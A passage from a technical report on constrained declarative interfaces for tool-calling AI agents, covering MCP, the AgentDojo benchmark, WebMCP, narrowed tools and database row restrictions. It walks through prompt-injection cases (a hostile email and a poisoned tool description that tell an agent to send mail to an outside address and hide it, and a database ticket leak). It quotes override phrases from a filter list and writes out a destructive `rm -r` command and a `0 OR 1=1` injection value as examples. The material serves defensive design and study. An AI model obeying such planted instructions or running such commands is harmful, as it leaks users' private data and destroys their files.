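# Constrained declarative interfaces for AI agents that call external tools

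## How an AI agent calls tools, and how a call goes wrong

A large language model takes in text and produces text. On its own, it can explain how to cancel a hotel booking but cannot cancel one. An AI agent is a language model connected to software that acts on some of what the model writes, such as by sending an email, retrieving a database record, or transferring money. The model triggers these actions through tool calls, which are structured requests for other software to run a named function with given arguments.

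With a constrained declarative interface, the agent states what it wants done in a small, checkable form, and separate software checks the statement and carries it out. Such interfaces are mostly a response to weaknesses of the ordinary tool call, in which the model chooses at each step what to run next.

### One tool call from start to finish

A developer begins by describing a function to the model. The stock example in OpenAI's *Function calling*, a guide for programmers, is a function named `get_weather`. Its definition consists of that name, a description in plain English and a schema, which is a formal list of the arguments that the function takes: a location, which may be any string of text, and a unit, which must be either "celsius" or "fahrenheit". The developer's application sends this definition to the model together with the user's question. When the user asks about the weather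 in Paris, the model can respond with a request of roughly this form:

```json
{ "name": "get_weather",
  "arguments": { "location": "Paris, France", "units": "celsius" } }
```

No tool has run yet. Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains, "The model never runs anything on its own." The application extracts the arguments from the request, queries a weather service and calls the model again with the whole history (the original question, the model's request and the result). The model then writes either an answer or another request, and the application repeats the cycle until the model makes no more requests. For a few tools, such as web search, the model's provider runs the code on its own servers, but the loop is otherwise the same.

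A schema restricts the format of a tool call but does little to ensure that the values make sense. OpenAI offers a strict mode that makes calls match the schema reliably, so an agent should not request a temperature in kelvin if the schema excludes that unit. But if an agent is supposed to email an accountant, a schema that only requires the address to be a string will also accept an attacker's address.

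The model's input also affects its next call. OpenAI inserts function definitions into the system message, which holds the standing instructions at the start of the conversation, and the application appends every tool result further down. The developer's rules, the tool descriptions, the user's request and tool results such as a stranger's email are therefore all in one stretch of text.

The software that executes the request must also be written carefully. In *Function calling using LLMs*, Prakash (2025) builds a shopping agent with three functions, which search for products, fetch a product's details and ask the user a clarifying question. A chain of if statements matches the requested name to one of these functions, and any other name produces an error message. Prakash warns against choosing functions with Python's `eval`, which executes text as program code. However, the first version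 of his example uses `eval` to unpack the arguments, so Python code in the arguments the model produces would run.

### What the Model Context Protocol standardises

Prakash's agent has its three functions written into its code, which limits what it can do and, as he notes, makes it easier to secure. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) replaces the fixed list with a lookup. Anthropic introduced MCP in 2024 to connect AI applications with outside systems, according to *MCP 2026 changes the rules* (Granados, 2026). It is now very widely used. The project's announcement of its July 2026 version reports close to half a billion monthly downloads of the main development kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

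The Model Context Protocol specification defines three roles. Hosts are applications that contain a model, servers offer tools and data, and clients are the connectors inside a host that talk to servers. Clients and servers exchange messages in JSON-RPC, an established format for calling functions on another machine. The specification's chapter *Tools* (Model Context Protocol, 2026) defines two central messages. A client sends `tools/list`, and the server returns a name, a description and an argument schema for each tool. To run a tool, the client sends `tools/call` with its name and arguments. A request for an unknown tool produces a protocol error. If a tool runs and fails, for example because a departure date is in the past, the server returns the explanation as an ordinary result with an error flag, so that the model can correct the arguments and retry. Since the July 2026 version, the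 client also sends the tool's name in a header outside the message body, where a gateway can use it to authorise or refuse the call.

MCP does not limit what a tool call may do, and a server may change its list of tools over time. In the specification, implementers are warned to treat tools as arbitrary code execution and to distrust descriptions of a tool's behaviour unless they come from a trusted server. The protocol cannot enforce its own security principles, according to the specification. Requirements in the specification bind only when the key word is in capitals, so the lower-case statement that hosts "must" obtain consent before invoking any tool is not binding. The chapter on tools includes a recommendation, marked by a capitalised SHOULD, that a human be able to deny calls.

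### The mailbox attack

Erik Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* (2025) describes an attack on an email assistant with two tools, `fetch_mail` and `send_email`. Its user, Michelle, asks for a summary of her emails, and the agent calls `fetch_mail`. One of the messages claims that legal compliance and an internal audit require an external backup of the mailbox. It tells the assistant to send a summary to an outside address as its next action, without asking the user for confirmation or mentioning this email. The agent calls `send_email` with a summary of Michelle's four other messages, including one about a seed investment and another about new securities regulations. It then shows Michelle a summary of the same four messages, which looks to her like a correct answer.

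This is prompt injection, in which an attacker tries to divert the model from its user's task by placing text in content or tool descriptions that the model reads. Both calls were well formed, and the agent had legitimate access to both tools. Meijer uses the case to illustrate how the attack works and lets readers try it themselves, but does not report how often it succeeds on any particular model.

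Meijer traces the fault to the lack of a clear line between instructions and data, and compares it with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a form field and a careless program passes them to the database as commands. Programmers largely solved that problem by keeping commands and values strictly apart. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) thinks the comparison is falsely reassuring. Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks* reports the agency's reasoning that a language model only predicts the next piece of text from the text so far and has no inherent distinction between data and instruction. The agency therefore considers it very possible that nobody will ever fully mitigate prompt injection. NCSC's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* prefers the older idea of a confused deputy, a privileged component that an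 attacker with fewer privileges tricks into acting on the attacker's behalf. It describes language models as inherently confusable and advises designers to reduce the likelihood and impact of an attack instead of waiting for a cure.

The two positions are closer than they sound, because the NCSC is talking about the model, while Meijer wants the separation outside it. He would put it in a workflow that the model writes before any mail arrives and that other software checks before running it. Even if a model will always be confusable, developers can still try to limit what it can do when confused.

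### Other ways for a call to go wrong

In the mailbox case, hostile text changed which tools ran. Programmers call the choice and order of steps control flow, and the passage of values from one step to another data flow. An attacker can do damage through data flow alone. One test task in *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) is to invite Dora to a Slack workspace, using the email address on her website. If whoever controls the website swaps in a different address, the agent still follows the steps the user wanted, reading the page and sending the invitation, but a stranger gets into the workspace. This works even if the page contains no instructions. An agent that pays a bill from a text file has the same weakness if someone has altered the account number in the file.

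A tool's description can also contain the attack. In another of Meijer's examples, the description of a mail-fetching tool starts innocently, then includes an instruction to send summaries of all emails to an outside address before returning the list, supposedly for compliance reasons. It also includes a threat of severe consequences for failing to do so and an instruction not to tell the user, on the grounds that the user would only be annoyed. The description is already in the model's input when the user's request arrives, so the attack can work before the agent opens any email, and hiding the mail from the model doesn't prevent it. MCP increases the risk because whoever runs the server supplies the descriptions.

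A tool call can also do harm without an attacker. Meijer imagines a `delete_file` tool that accepts wildcard patterns. A user asks for `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` to be deleted, and the model, choosing the shorter program, calls the tool once with `*.txt`, which deletes every text file in the folder. This call would pass a check that tested only whether the two files were gone, so Meijer adds a condition that everything else must stay unchanged.

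*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) describes a case that is harder to catch. A calendar agent can list events, update them and send email. Its user enters an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, and the appointment clashes with a work meeting. The agent proposes moving the meeting, the user agrees, and the agent emails colleagues about the change, including the details of the appointment. Each tool worked correctly, but the agent copied private information from the calendar into the email, and the user had approved only the new time, not the email's wording. *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, describes a simpler case in which a model invents a wrong parameter and sensitive data ends up in a public log.

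### How AgentDojo measures the damage

Much of the evidence on defences against these failures comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark (a standard set of test tasks) from ETH Zurich and the company Invariant Labs. Debenedetti and colleagues built four simulated environments with 74 tools in total and filled each with invented data. The benchmark pairs every user task (an ordinary request) with every injection task (an attacker's goal, such as emailing out a security code) in the same environment, and each pair is one security case.

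| Suite | What the tools do | User tasks | Injection tasks | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | email, calendar, cloud drive | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | messages, web pages, files | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | flights, hotels, restaurants, car rental | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | payments, bank statements | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | | 97 | 27 | 629 |

The user's task can take as many as 18 tool calls, and the attacker's text sits in data that the agent will read while doing it, such as one of the emails it has to search. Ordinary program code scores each run. For each user task, one function inspects the agent's output and the state of the environment before and after the run, and a similar function checks whether the attacker's goal was achieved. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against using a second language model as judge because a successful injection might hijack the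 judge too.

Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which the agent completes the user's task with no adversarial side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker achieves their goal. A low attack success rate means little without the utility figures, because an agent that does nothing would score zero.

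The first results, from 2024, are dated but give a sense of scale. Models completed fewer than 66% of the tasks even without an attack, and attacks on the best-performing agents succeeded in fewer than 25% of cases. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, possibly because weaker ones often failed at the attacker's task too.

AgentDojo covers only some of the failures above. Its attacks are instructions planted in data, as in the mailbox example. A poisoned tool description or a quietly altered address falls outside that pattern, and mistakes an agent makes without being attacked mostly show up as lost utility. Debenedetti and colleagues also warn that it is extremely easy to build a defence that stops one specific attack and fails against the next, which is why they made the benchmark extensible. A score of zero against a fixed set of attacks therefore doesn't guarantee that a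 defence will stop other attacks.

### User confirmation and text filters

One safeguard is to ask the user before each call. Michelle might have refused if a prompt had named the outside address. But Meijer compares such prompts to cookie banners because people who see them constantly stop reading and click "Allow". Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this approval fatigue.

Users of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*. That figure alone proves little, because most prompts probably concern harmless routine commands. A test with 1,053 paid testers provides better evidence. Partway through each session, according to the design that Simon Willison quotes, a clearly dangerous command replaced one permission prompt. The website Hyrax reports that the testers caught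 it in 143 cases, or 13.6%, and that the rate fell from roughly 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic published the test to support letting a classifier (a model that sorts commands into safe and dangerous) approve commands by default, and paid testers have less to lose than people working on their own files. Even allowing for both, 13.6% is a very poor detection rate for a final safeguard.

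Hyrax also cites Anthropic's production data, in which users reject 39% of the plans the agent proposes. Hyrax infers that developers read plans carefully but approve single prompts by reflex. Some of those rejections may only mean that the plan was not what the user had in mind, but the gap between plans and single prompts is wide enough to suggest that what people are asked to approve affects how carefully they review it.

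Automatic filters do not tire, but they miss some threats. Prakash's shopping agent uses the simplest kind, a list of eight suspicious phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" and "act as". This list would miss the hostile email in Meijer's example, which contains none of the phrases. It would also flag the harmless request "please contact Ashley", because the letters of "act as" run across the last two words. Prakash presents the list as a basic version to build on, and suggests using a second model as a subtler filter. Model-based filters do better. The classifier in Anthropic's test blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands and missed 116, and in AgentDojo's first experiments a separate attack detector reduced the attack success rate to 8%. Doshi and colleagues object that a persistent attacker may need only one success and can tailor the attempt to the filter. Some failures also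 contain no suspicious text for a filter to detect. The address on Dora's website looks like any other address, and `*.txt` is an ordinary argument.

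## What "declarative" and "constrained" mean for a tool interface

A constrained declarative interface limits what the model can usefully write, whereas confirmation prompts and text filters are meant to catch a bad tool call after the model has written it. An interface can be declarative without being constrained, and vice versa.

An interface is declarative if the agent submits data describing the operations or result it wants, and a separate program decides how to carry out the request. It is constrained if its language cannot express actions outside a defined set, or if a checker rejects them.

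Programmers often use "declarative" more strictly, for programs that describe a result and leave out the control flow. Few agent interfaces meet that definition. For example, a plan to fetch the mail, summarise it and show the summary fixes the order of the steps. This report still calls it declarative because the plan is data that another program reads and carries out.

### Hard cases

Suppose an agent has a tool named `run_shell`, which takes one argument, a command for the operating system. The model's request is tidy JSON and matches the schema:

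```json
{ "name": "run_shell",
  "arguments": { "command": "rm -r /home/michelle/mail" } }
```

This request deletes Michelle's mail folder, and another request to the same interface could upload it to a stranger. The interface is barely constrained, even though its requests are structured. The outer request is data, but its argument is a shell program, so a checker that parses only the JSON cannot determine what the command will do.

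SQL, the standard language for databases, is declarative. The statement `DELETE FROM customers` describes a result, an empty table, and the database determines how to remove the rows. The declarative form does not protect the customers' records, but permissions can. If the agent's database account is read-only, the database rejects the statement.

When Python runs in a sandbox (a closed environment without network access or outside files), the constraint comes entirely from the sandbox. A Python program can try to open a network connection, and it fails only because the sandbox has no network. A language can also constrain a program that isn't declarative in the strict sense. For example, an agent might write ordinary code, with loops and steps in a fixed order, in a language whose type checker rejects any program that would pass private data to an unapproved function.

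SPL (Structured Prompt Language) is harder to classify. *Structured Prompt Language* (2026) presents it as a query language, modelled on SQL, for managing what goes into a model's limited input. Gong (2026), in *Orchestrating Workflows with Declarative Deterministic—Probabilistic Composition*, describes a version for whole workflows. `SELECT` gathers context, `GENERATE` calls a model, `SOLVE` sends an expression to a Python process for exact calculation, and `ASSERT` tests a condition before the workflow continues. The workflow file states what each step computes, and the user chooses the model and calculation software when starting the workflow.

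That makes SPL declarative in the looser sense, although it also has variables and loops. Its grammar excludes little, because `ASSERT` accepts any Python expression that evaluates to true or false. Gong relies for safety on running the Python process in a sandbox that cannot reach the host's files or network. A faster option runs code inside the main process with Python's `exec`, and the sandbox argument does not apply to it.

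### Who declares what

Papers differ in what they call "declarative". A developer can declare an agent's configuration, such as its model, tools and any fixed sequence of steps. The agent can declare a plan for the task it has just received. An operator, meaning whoever is responsible for the running system, can declare a policy on which actions are allowed, regardless of the agent's plan.

How far a declaration can be trusted depends on who wrote it. A configuration exists before any hostile email arrives, so the email cannot rewrite it, but the configuration may still leave the model a lot of freedom within a step. A plan is written by a model that may make mistakes or have read hostile text, so other software needs to check it. That software checks the plan against a policy, which gives no protection if the agent can edit it.

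In *SPA* (2026), the agent declares its plan in a small JSON language that excludes arbitrary computation, so a checker can judge the plan without running it. *Soteria* (2026) uses declared policies. Each tool has a contract, with one condition on its inputs and another on its inputs and outputs together, and a set of specifications defines correct behaviour for the agent. A separate condition on the final state of the environment defines whether the user's task succeeded, so an agent could satisfy every specification and still fail to cancel a reservation it was supposed to cancel.

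The same language can serve for more than one of these. A developer can write an SPL file by hand as configuration, or use a companion tool, text2spl, which has a model generate SPL from a plain-language description. A generated file needs the same checking as any other model-written plan.

### PayPal's workflow language

*A Declarative Language for Building And Orchestrating LLM-Powered Agent Workflows* (Daunis, 2025) describes a configuration language that PayPal uses for shopping agents. A developer builds a workflow from a short list of step types. For example, `setValue` stores a value, `forEach` repeats steps over a list, `when` branches on a condition, and `function` calls code that the developer has registered. A `toolRequest` step gives a model a set of tools to choose from. The compiler turns the workflow into JSON, which servers written in Java, Python or Go can execute. Before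 anything runs, the compiler checks for unreachable steps, undefined variables and circular dependencies, and compares tool calls with their declared parameters.

Daunis reports a 60% reduction in development time in the abstract. The reduction in the evaluation, which Daunis calls preliminary, is 67%, from 48 hours for a conventional implementation to 16. Adding a tool or modifying a workflow took 2 hours instead of 8.5. On 1,000 real customer sessions, with the same model and tools, the task success rate was 89%, compared with 78% for the conventional implementation. This is one comparison at one company, and Daunis does not report how many developers took part or whether the same people built both versions, so the exact percentages deserve little weight.

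The claim that non-engineers can modify agent behaviour "safely" has less evidence behind it. Daunis reports no study of non-engineers making changes and no test with hostile input. The paper instead argues that changes should be safe because the compiler catches malformed pipelines, the language excludes unbounded recursion and arbitrary code, and a team can revert a bad configuration instantly. It also lists caps on the number of tool calls, restricted access to variables and human confirmation of critical actions, but reports no measurements that test them.

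Most of these measures protect against broken pipelines, but not necessarily against harmful ones. Suppose a marketing employee adds the checkout tool to a step in which a model reads product descriptions from outside sellers. The pipeline compiles because all the variables and types are correct. Inside that step, the model still chooses its own tool calls, as Michelle's email assistant did, and a hostile product description could steer it towards a purchase. Human confirmation might stop the purchase, but that protection doesn't depend on the interface being declarative.

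Registered functions weaken the case further because they run ordinary code that can read and change the pipeline's variables. Daunis concedes that using them as an escape hatch breaks the declarative paradigm. The evidence supports "safely" in the narrow sense that a non-engineer's mistake is less likely to crash the pipeline and is easy to undo.

### The argument for declarative form

The argument that declarative interfaces make agents safer relies on a small language expressing fewer actions, so it is an argument for constraint. For example, if an assistant's language has a step for showing a summary but none for sending mail, a hostile email cannot make the assistant send mail. The argument applies equally well to a typed program, and it fails for a small declarative language that includes `run_shell`.

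The next premise is that declarative form makes dependencies visible. If each step names the values it uses, a checker can trace the text of an email from the step that fetched it to a step that would send it elsewhere. *The Rule of Least Power* (Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn, 2006), a finding approved by the World Wide Web Consortium's Technical Architecture Group, explains why this is easier in some languages than in others. It ranks languages by power, from HTML and the contents of most databases up to Java and C. Some versions of SQL are Turing complete, meaning they can express any computation a computer can perform, and others are not. There is typically no way to determine what an arbitrary program in a Turing-complete language will do except by running it. Less powerful languages are also usually easier to secure, according to the finding.

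Their rule is about publishing on the Web, where other people's software must be able to reuse the information. Kevin Braun, whose message Mendelsohn (2012) quotes, did not believe the rule was meant as a broad architectural principle. But the point about analysing programs also holds outside the Web.

The last premise is that a checker can refuse a harmful request before any of it runs. When a model makes its calls one at a time, a checker can check the third call only after the first two have taken effect. If the model submits a complete plan, the checker can reject all three together. This prevents harm only if someone has correctly specified what counts as harmful. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of the field, describes fragility at every stage: specifications may be wrong, verification may rely on an inaccurate model of the system, and enforcement may block individual unsafe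 actions while the task as a whole remains unsafe.

If all three premises hold, either the agent cannot express a harmful action or the system refuses it in time. Declarative form alone provides only visibility. The rest depends on a well-chosen set of actions and a correct policy.

### What a smaller language costs

The main objection is that a language too small for harmful actions will also be too small for some useful ones, so the agent will complete fewer tasks. Lim, Bin Sharudin and colleagues (2026), in *Declarative Skills for AI Agents in Knowledge-Grounded Tool-Use Workflows*, state the formal version. Let $\Pi_B$ be the set of behaviours open to an unrestricted agent and $\Pi_I$ the set open to the same model when software permits only some actions at each turn. Let $r$ be 1 if the task succeeds and 0 if it fails. Since $\Pi_I$ is a subset of $\Pi_B$,

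$$\sup_{\pi \in \Pi_I} \mathbb{E}[r] \leq \sup_{\pi \in \Pi_B} \mathbb{E}[r].$$

The inequality means that the best restricted behaviour cannot have a higher expected success rate than the best unrestricted behaviour. Real models fall well short of both, however, and a model that often picks the wrong tool may complete more tasks when it has fewer tools to choose from. Experiments are therefore needed to measure the restriction's actual effect on success rate.

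Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn warn that a language must be powerful enough for its problem, and that clumsy workarounds for one that is too limited add complexity. PayPal's escape hatch looks like an example.

Models must also be able to write the required form. Gong gave ten models 20 mathematics problems, three times each, in two versions. In one, the model broke the problem into steps for symbolic mathematics software, and a run passed if the software executed every step. Pass rates ranged from 32% to 93%. In the other, the model answered alone and any non-empty response passed, so pass rates ranged from 77% to 100%. As Gong acknowledges, the two versions measure different things, so the gap between them is not a loss of mathematical accuracy. The spread among the models is more informative. Two small models, phi3 and gemma4:e2b, wrote fully executable steps in 32% and 93% of runs respectively,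 although phi3 always produced an answer when working alone.

### An experiment with "declarative" and "imperative" agents

Lim and colleagues measured the drop in completed tasks more directly, using 97 simulated customer-service tasks at a bank. A task counted as completed only if the agent made all the required tool calls and left the database in exactly the right state. Five models attempted the tasks under two conditions, one with the relevant bank documents in the prompt and one where the agent had to search for them.

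Each model ran as three agents. The baseline had the tools and the benchmark's standard instructions. The "declarative" agent also had three skill files, which are plain-English documents about banking procedures, customer conversations and searching. The "imperative" agent ran inside a state machine, a program that moved it through fixed phases (such as verification, planning and execution) and allowed only certain tools in each.

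Neither label describes a tool interface of the kind defined earlier. Skill files advise the model but do not restrict which actions it can choose, and no separate program checks whether it follows them. The agent called imperative is the constrained one. The experiment therefore compares two ways for a developer to supply procedures, and does not test plans that an agent declares.

The table shows the change in completed tasks from the same model's baseline, in percentage points. One asterisk marks p < 0.05, two mark p < 0.01 and three mark p < 0.001.

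| Model | Skill files, documents supplied | Skill files, agent searches | State machine, documents supplied | State machine, agent searches |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-v4-Pro | +2.2 | −1.1 | −27.3*** | −14.1** |
| DeepSeek-v4-Flash | −3.3 | +4.2 | −18.7** | −1.1 |
| Gemini-3.1-Flash-Lite | 0.0 | +5.2 | −13.7* | +1.0 |
| Qwen3.5-Flash | −3.1 | +7.3 | −2.1 | +2.1 |
| Haiku-4.5 | −9.4* | 0.0 | −20.2*** | −2.1 |

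The significance test uses only the tasks on which one agent succeeded and the other failed. Over all ten combinations of model and condition, the agent with skill files succeeded on 73 of these tasks and failed on 71 (p = 0.93), so skill files made no detectable difference on average. An earlier version of the paper reported gains on four of the five models, but paired testing did not confirm that pattern.

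Lim and colleagues now argue that skill files help when the agent has to search. In that condition, skill files had 37 wins and 22 losses, compared with 36 wins and 49 losses when the documents were supplied. The two win rates differ significantly (p = 0.016). The benefit of skill files is plausible but not established, because the gain in the search condition is not significant on its own (p = 0.067) and no single model improved significantly.

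The state machine won 46 tasks and lost 132. This result is weaker support than it looks for the objection that constraint reduces task completion, because the state machine did much more than restrict actions. It also inserted new instructions at each phase, required replies of a particular type and retried failed calls. When it assigned the wrong phase, the model could even make changes before verifying the customer's identity, which the state machine was supposed to prevent.

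In a follow-up test, Lim and colleagues isolated that restriction by adding it alone to the baseline agent. They enforced it on the tool calls themselves, so no call that changes data could run until the agent had verified the customer's identity. The test used DeepSeek-v4-Pro with the documents supplied. The original baseline agent broke the rule in 4.3% of tasks and the state machine in 4.4%. With the rule enforced, none of 467 changes ran before verification. The agent completed 49.0% of tasks, statistically indistinguishable from the baseline's 46.2% and far above the state machine's 20.0%. The average cost per task rose from about 0.9 to 2.2 US cents.

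By comparison, when the documents were supplied, skill files reduced the share of tasks in which Haiku-4.5 made a premature change from 41.7% to 15.6%. This is a large reduction, but skill files do not guarantee that the model will avoid premature changes, and it completed significantly fewer tasks in the same condition.

The follow-up covers only one model and one rule, but it shows that a constraint need not reduce task success. The experiment as a whole measures task success and adherence to procedure, not security, and included no attacker or planted instructions. Once the agent has verified the customer, the rule allows every later change, including one prompted by hostile text.

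## Narrow tools and restricted queries over data

The identity check in the bank experiment controlled when the agent could change data, but not what it could change. A developer can also limit what it can change by narrowing a tool until its arguments cannot express a harmful call. This is the simplest kind of constrained interface, because software can check each call without knowing what the agent did before.

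### Narrowing one tool in stages

Suppose an agent's job is to forward suppliers' invoices to a company's accountant. Any of these four tools would let it do so.

| Tool | What the model writes | Harm the model can no longer express | Harm that remains |
|---|---|---|---|
| `run_shell` | any command | none, beyond the limits of its operating-system account | deleting files, installing software, uploading data |
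| `send_email` | an address, a subject and a message | deleting files, running programs | sending any text to anyone |
| `email_colleague` | one of three listed names, and a message | writing to a stranger | sending confidential or misleading text to a colleague |
| `forward_invoice` | an invoice number | choosing a recipient, writing a message | forwarding the wrong invoice, or a forged one |

`send_email` has typed arguments, which means the schema gives each one a name and a kind of value, here text. `email_colleague` adds an enumeration, a closed list of permitted values. With `forward_invoice`, the server gets the accountant's address from its own settings and attaches the stored file. A hostile email cannot redirect the invoice because the call has no address argument.

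Each step moves a decision from the model to the server, so the protection depends on the server's data. An attacker who changes the accountant's address in the company's settings will receive the invoices without any prompt injection. The server has to enforce the list of names, because a model can write a name that isn't on it. Narrower tools are also less flexible. An agent with only `forward_invoice` cannot tell the accountant that an invoice looks wrong.

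A tool's credentials also need to be narrow. PocketOS, which makes software for car rental firms, lost its production database when a programming agent deleted a storage volume with a single call to the hosting provider, Railway. The agent was supposed to be working in a test environment, according to ITPro's *Nine seconds was all it took for an AI agent to wipe a startup's database*. It later wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only that environment, although a model's account of its own reasons is weak evidence. Techzine's *AI agent deleted production environment after acting autonomously* adds that the access token was intended for a limited function but had broad permissions. With a token valid only for the test environment, the agent could not have deleted the production volume. Railway has since recovered the data, ITPro reports, and deletions through its API can now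 be undone for 48 hours.

Tools that only read data can be too broad in the same way. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 2026) describes a coding assistant that could not find its configuration file during a routine code review. It read all the variables on the computer and leaked live passwords. If its tool had returned only a single named setting, it would have had much less to leak.

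A narrow interface limits what an agent can request, but the code behind the tool may do more than its description suggests. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) give the example of a tool that is supposed to write a file but also reports the size of the file's contents to a metrics service. They propose analysing each tool's code for effects such as network access, and wrapping those effects in small sandboxes that check them at run time. So far they have reported preliminary experiments with one real tool server.

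### Constrained decoding

Software can also enforce a schema while the model is still writing the call. A language model writes one token at a time, a token being a word or part of a word. At each step it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the surrounding software picks one. In constrained decoding, that software first works out which tokens could still lead to text that fits a given grammar or schema. It masks the rest by setting their probability to zero. If $x$ is the text so far, $p(t \mid x)$ the model's probability for token $t$, and $A(x)$ the set of allowed tokens, the new probability is

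$$p'(t \mid x) = \begin{cases} \dfrac{p(t \mid x)}{\sum_{u \in A(x)} p(u \mid x)} & \text{if } t \in A(x), \\ 0 & \text{otherwise.} \end{cases}$$

In the weather example, the unit must be "celsius" or "fahrenheit". After the opening quotation mark, the decoder allows only tokens that begin one of those words. Once the model has written "cel", it can only finish "celsius". The call will match the schema unless the model hits a length limit before completing it.

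The guarantee covers only the form of the call, so "Paris, Texas" passes even if the user meant "Paris, France". Masking can also hide a mistake. If a user asks for kelvin and the model tries to comply, the mask forces it to write one of the two allowed units instead, and the application receives a valid request with no sign that the unit changed. Adding a value such as "unsupported" to the list at least gives the model a way to decline.

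The same limit applies to whole database queries. PICARD, a method from 2021, rejects partial output that cannot be extended into valid SQL. Wu (2026) points out in *Never the Number* that PICARD cannot guarantee that the query answers the user's question. Wu cites a 2025 result in which an agent with a reasoning model solved 21.3% of tasks on Spider 2.0, a benchmark built from real industrial databases, compared with 91.2% on the older and simpler Spider. Current models probably do better, but the errors Wu lists for such databases, such as choosing the wrong table or missing an unstated assumption, all produce valid SQL.

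### Web forms as tools

Many websites already have narrow tools, such as web forms with fixed fields and drop-down lists. Chrome for Developers (2026) describes WebMCP, a proposed standard that lets a page declare its functions as tools for an agent in the browser, so the agent doesn't have to guess what each button does.

In the declarative version, a developer adds a name and description to an ordinary form, and the browser translates its fields into a schema. *Declarative API* (Klepper and Beaufort, 2026) shows a customer-support form whose two name boxes become free-text arguments and whose drop-down list becomes an enumeration of three support teams. When an agent calls the tool, the browser fills in the visible form and the user clicks Submit. The developer can remove the need for that click by adding the `toolautosubmit` attribute.

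Security guidance from Chrome for Developers (2026) advises sites to attach hints to their tools, for example that a tool only reads data, has serious consequences, or includes untrusted content in its output. The browser or agent can use these hints to decide when to ask the user for confirmation. However, a dishonest shop could label its purchase tool as read-only. WebMCP's narrow tools therefore mainly help honest sites receive well-formed requests. They do much less for a user whose agent visits a hostile page, because that page supplies both the schema and the code behind it.

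WebMCP is still experimental. The Web Machine Learning Community Group's draft, *WebMCP*, is neither a W3C standard nor on the track to become one. By June 2026, the group was ready to request reviews from W3C's architecture, privacy and security groups, according to W3C's *25 webmachinelearning minutes* (2026). Chrome and Edge offer WebMCP through origin trials, which Chrome for Developers (2026) describes as time-limited programmes for testing experimental features on live sites. Nabors (2026), in *Google and OpenAI Want Your Site to Talk to Agents*, reports that Chrome's trial runs through version 156 and that the draft's commands have changed repeatedly.

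Companies are adopting WebMCP before it is a standard. It has been on by default in all Shopify shops since August 2026, according to Journal du Net's *Comment ouvrir votre site aux agents IA avec WebMCP*, although Claude and Gemini still had no native support in October. In early November, an unofficial guide, *WebMCP*, listed ChatGPT's desktop application as supporting it and the positions of Firefox and Safari as still under discussion. The form version is the least settled part. The guide says the group is still exploring it, and the specification defines only the JavaScript version.

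### One customer's orders

Databases need a different kind of narrowing, because a single query language gives access to everything in them. Suppose customer 4172 logs in to an online shop and asks its support agent where her order is. The agent should be able to see her orders but not other customers' orders.

In the first design, the agent has a tool named `run_sql` that accepts any query. The model writes a sensible one:

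```sql
SELECT order_id, status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 4172;
```

The tool would also run `SELECT * FROM orders`, which returns every customer's orders. The model might write that query because of an instruction in a message, or because it left out the condition by mistake. Constrained decoding would not help, since the query is valid SQL. A read-only account would prevent the agent from deleting orders but not from reading them all. PromptQL's *How to Give AI Agents Safe Access to Warehouse Data* gives a more serious example, in which an agent with a read-only account joins customers' email addresses to their prescription histories.

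In the second design, the agent has a tool named `get_order_status`, which takes only an order number. The server runs a query that the developer wrote in advance:

```sql
SELECT order_id, status, delivery_date
FROM orders
WHERE order_id = :order_id
  AND customer_id = :session_customer;
```

The model supplies `order_id`, and the server fills in `session_customer` from the customer's login session. If the model supplies the ID of another customer's order, the query returns no rows. Text in the chat cannot change `session_customer`, because the tool has no argument for it.

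This is a parameterised query: the database receives the SQL and the values separately and never interprets a value as SQL. It therefore treats an order number of `0 OR 1=1` as an invalid number rather than a condition that matches every row. But parameters alone would not restrict the agent to one customer's orders. If the tool also took the customer's number as an argument, the model could write 4173 and the database would return that customer's order. The server prevents this by not taking the customer's number from the model.

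### Views, row-level security and approved queries

The database itself can enforce some of these limits, whatever SQL the agent writes. A view is a stored query that can be queried like a table. A view for the support agent could include order numbers, statuses and delivery dates but leave out payment details. If the agent's account can read only that view, the agent cannot reach the payment details. PromptQL, a vendor of data-access software, recommends a separate view for each of an agent's tasks, with personal fields masked.

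A view of this kind hides columns but still shows every customer's rows. Row-level security restricts the rows. The developer attaches a rule to a table, and the database applies it to every query from the accounts it covers. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, the rule might be:

```sql
CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders FOR SELECT
USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer_id')::int);
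```

Once the developer has enabled row-level security on the table and the server has set `app.customer_id` to 4172, `SELECT * FROM orders` returns only her orders. The agent can then write its own queries about them, which `get_order_status` does not allow. But PostgreSQL lets ordinary accounts change a custom setting like this one, even from within a `SELECT`, so a hijacked agent that can send arbitrary SQL could switch to customer 4173 before running its query. This restriction is reliable only if it depends on an identity that the agent's SQL cannot change. Some accounts, such as administrators, are exempt from row-level security.

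The strictest option is to have the agent choose by name from a list of pre-approved queries, such as `get_order_status`. If a customer asks which of her orders arrived late last year and no query on the list covers that, the agent cannot answer until a developer adds one.

### A leak through an exempt account

The best-known leak through an over-broad database connection is a demonstration by a team at General Analysis, who used an MCP server to connect the programming agent Cursor to a test database on the hosting service Supabase. In their scenario, a developer asks the agent to list the latest support tickets, one of which contains an attacker's instructions. The agent follows them, reading private data from elsewhere in the database and writing it into a field the attacker can see.

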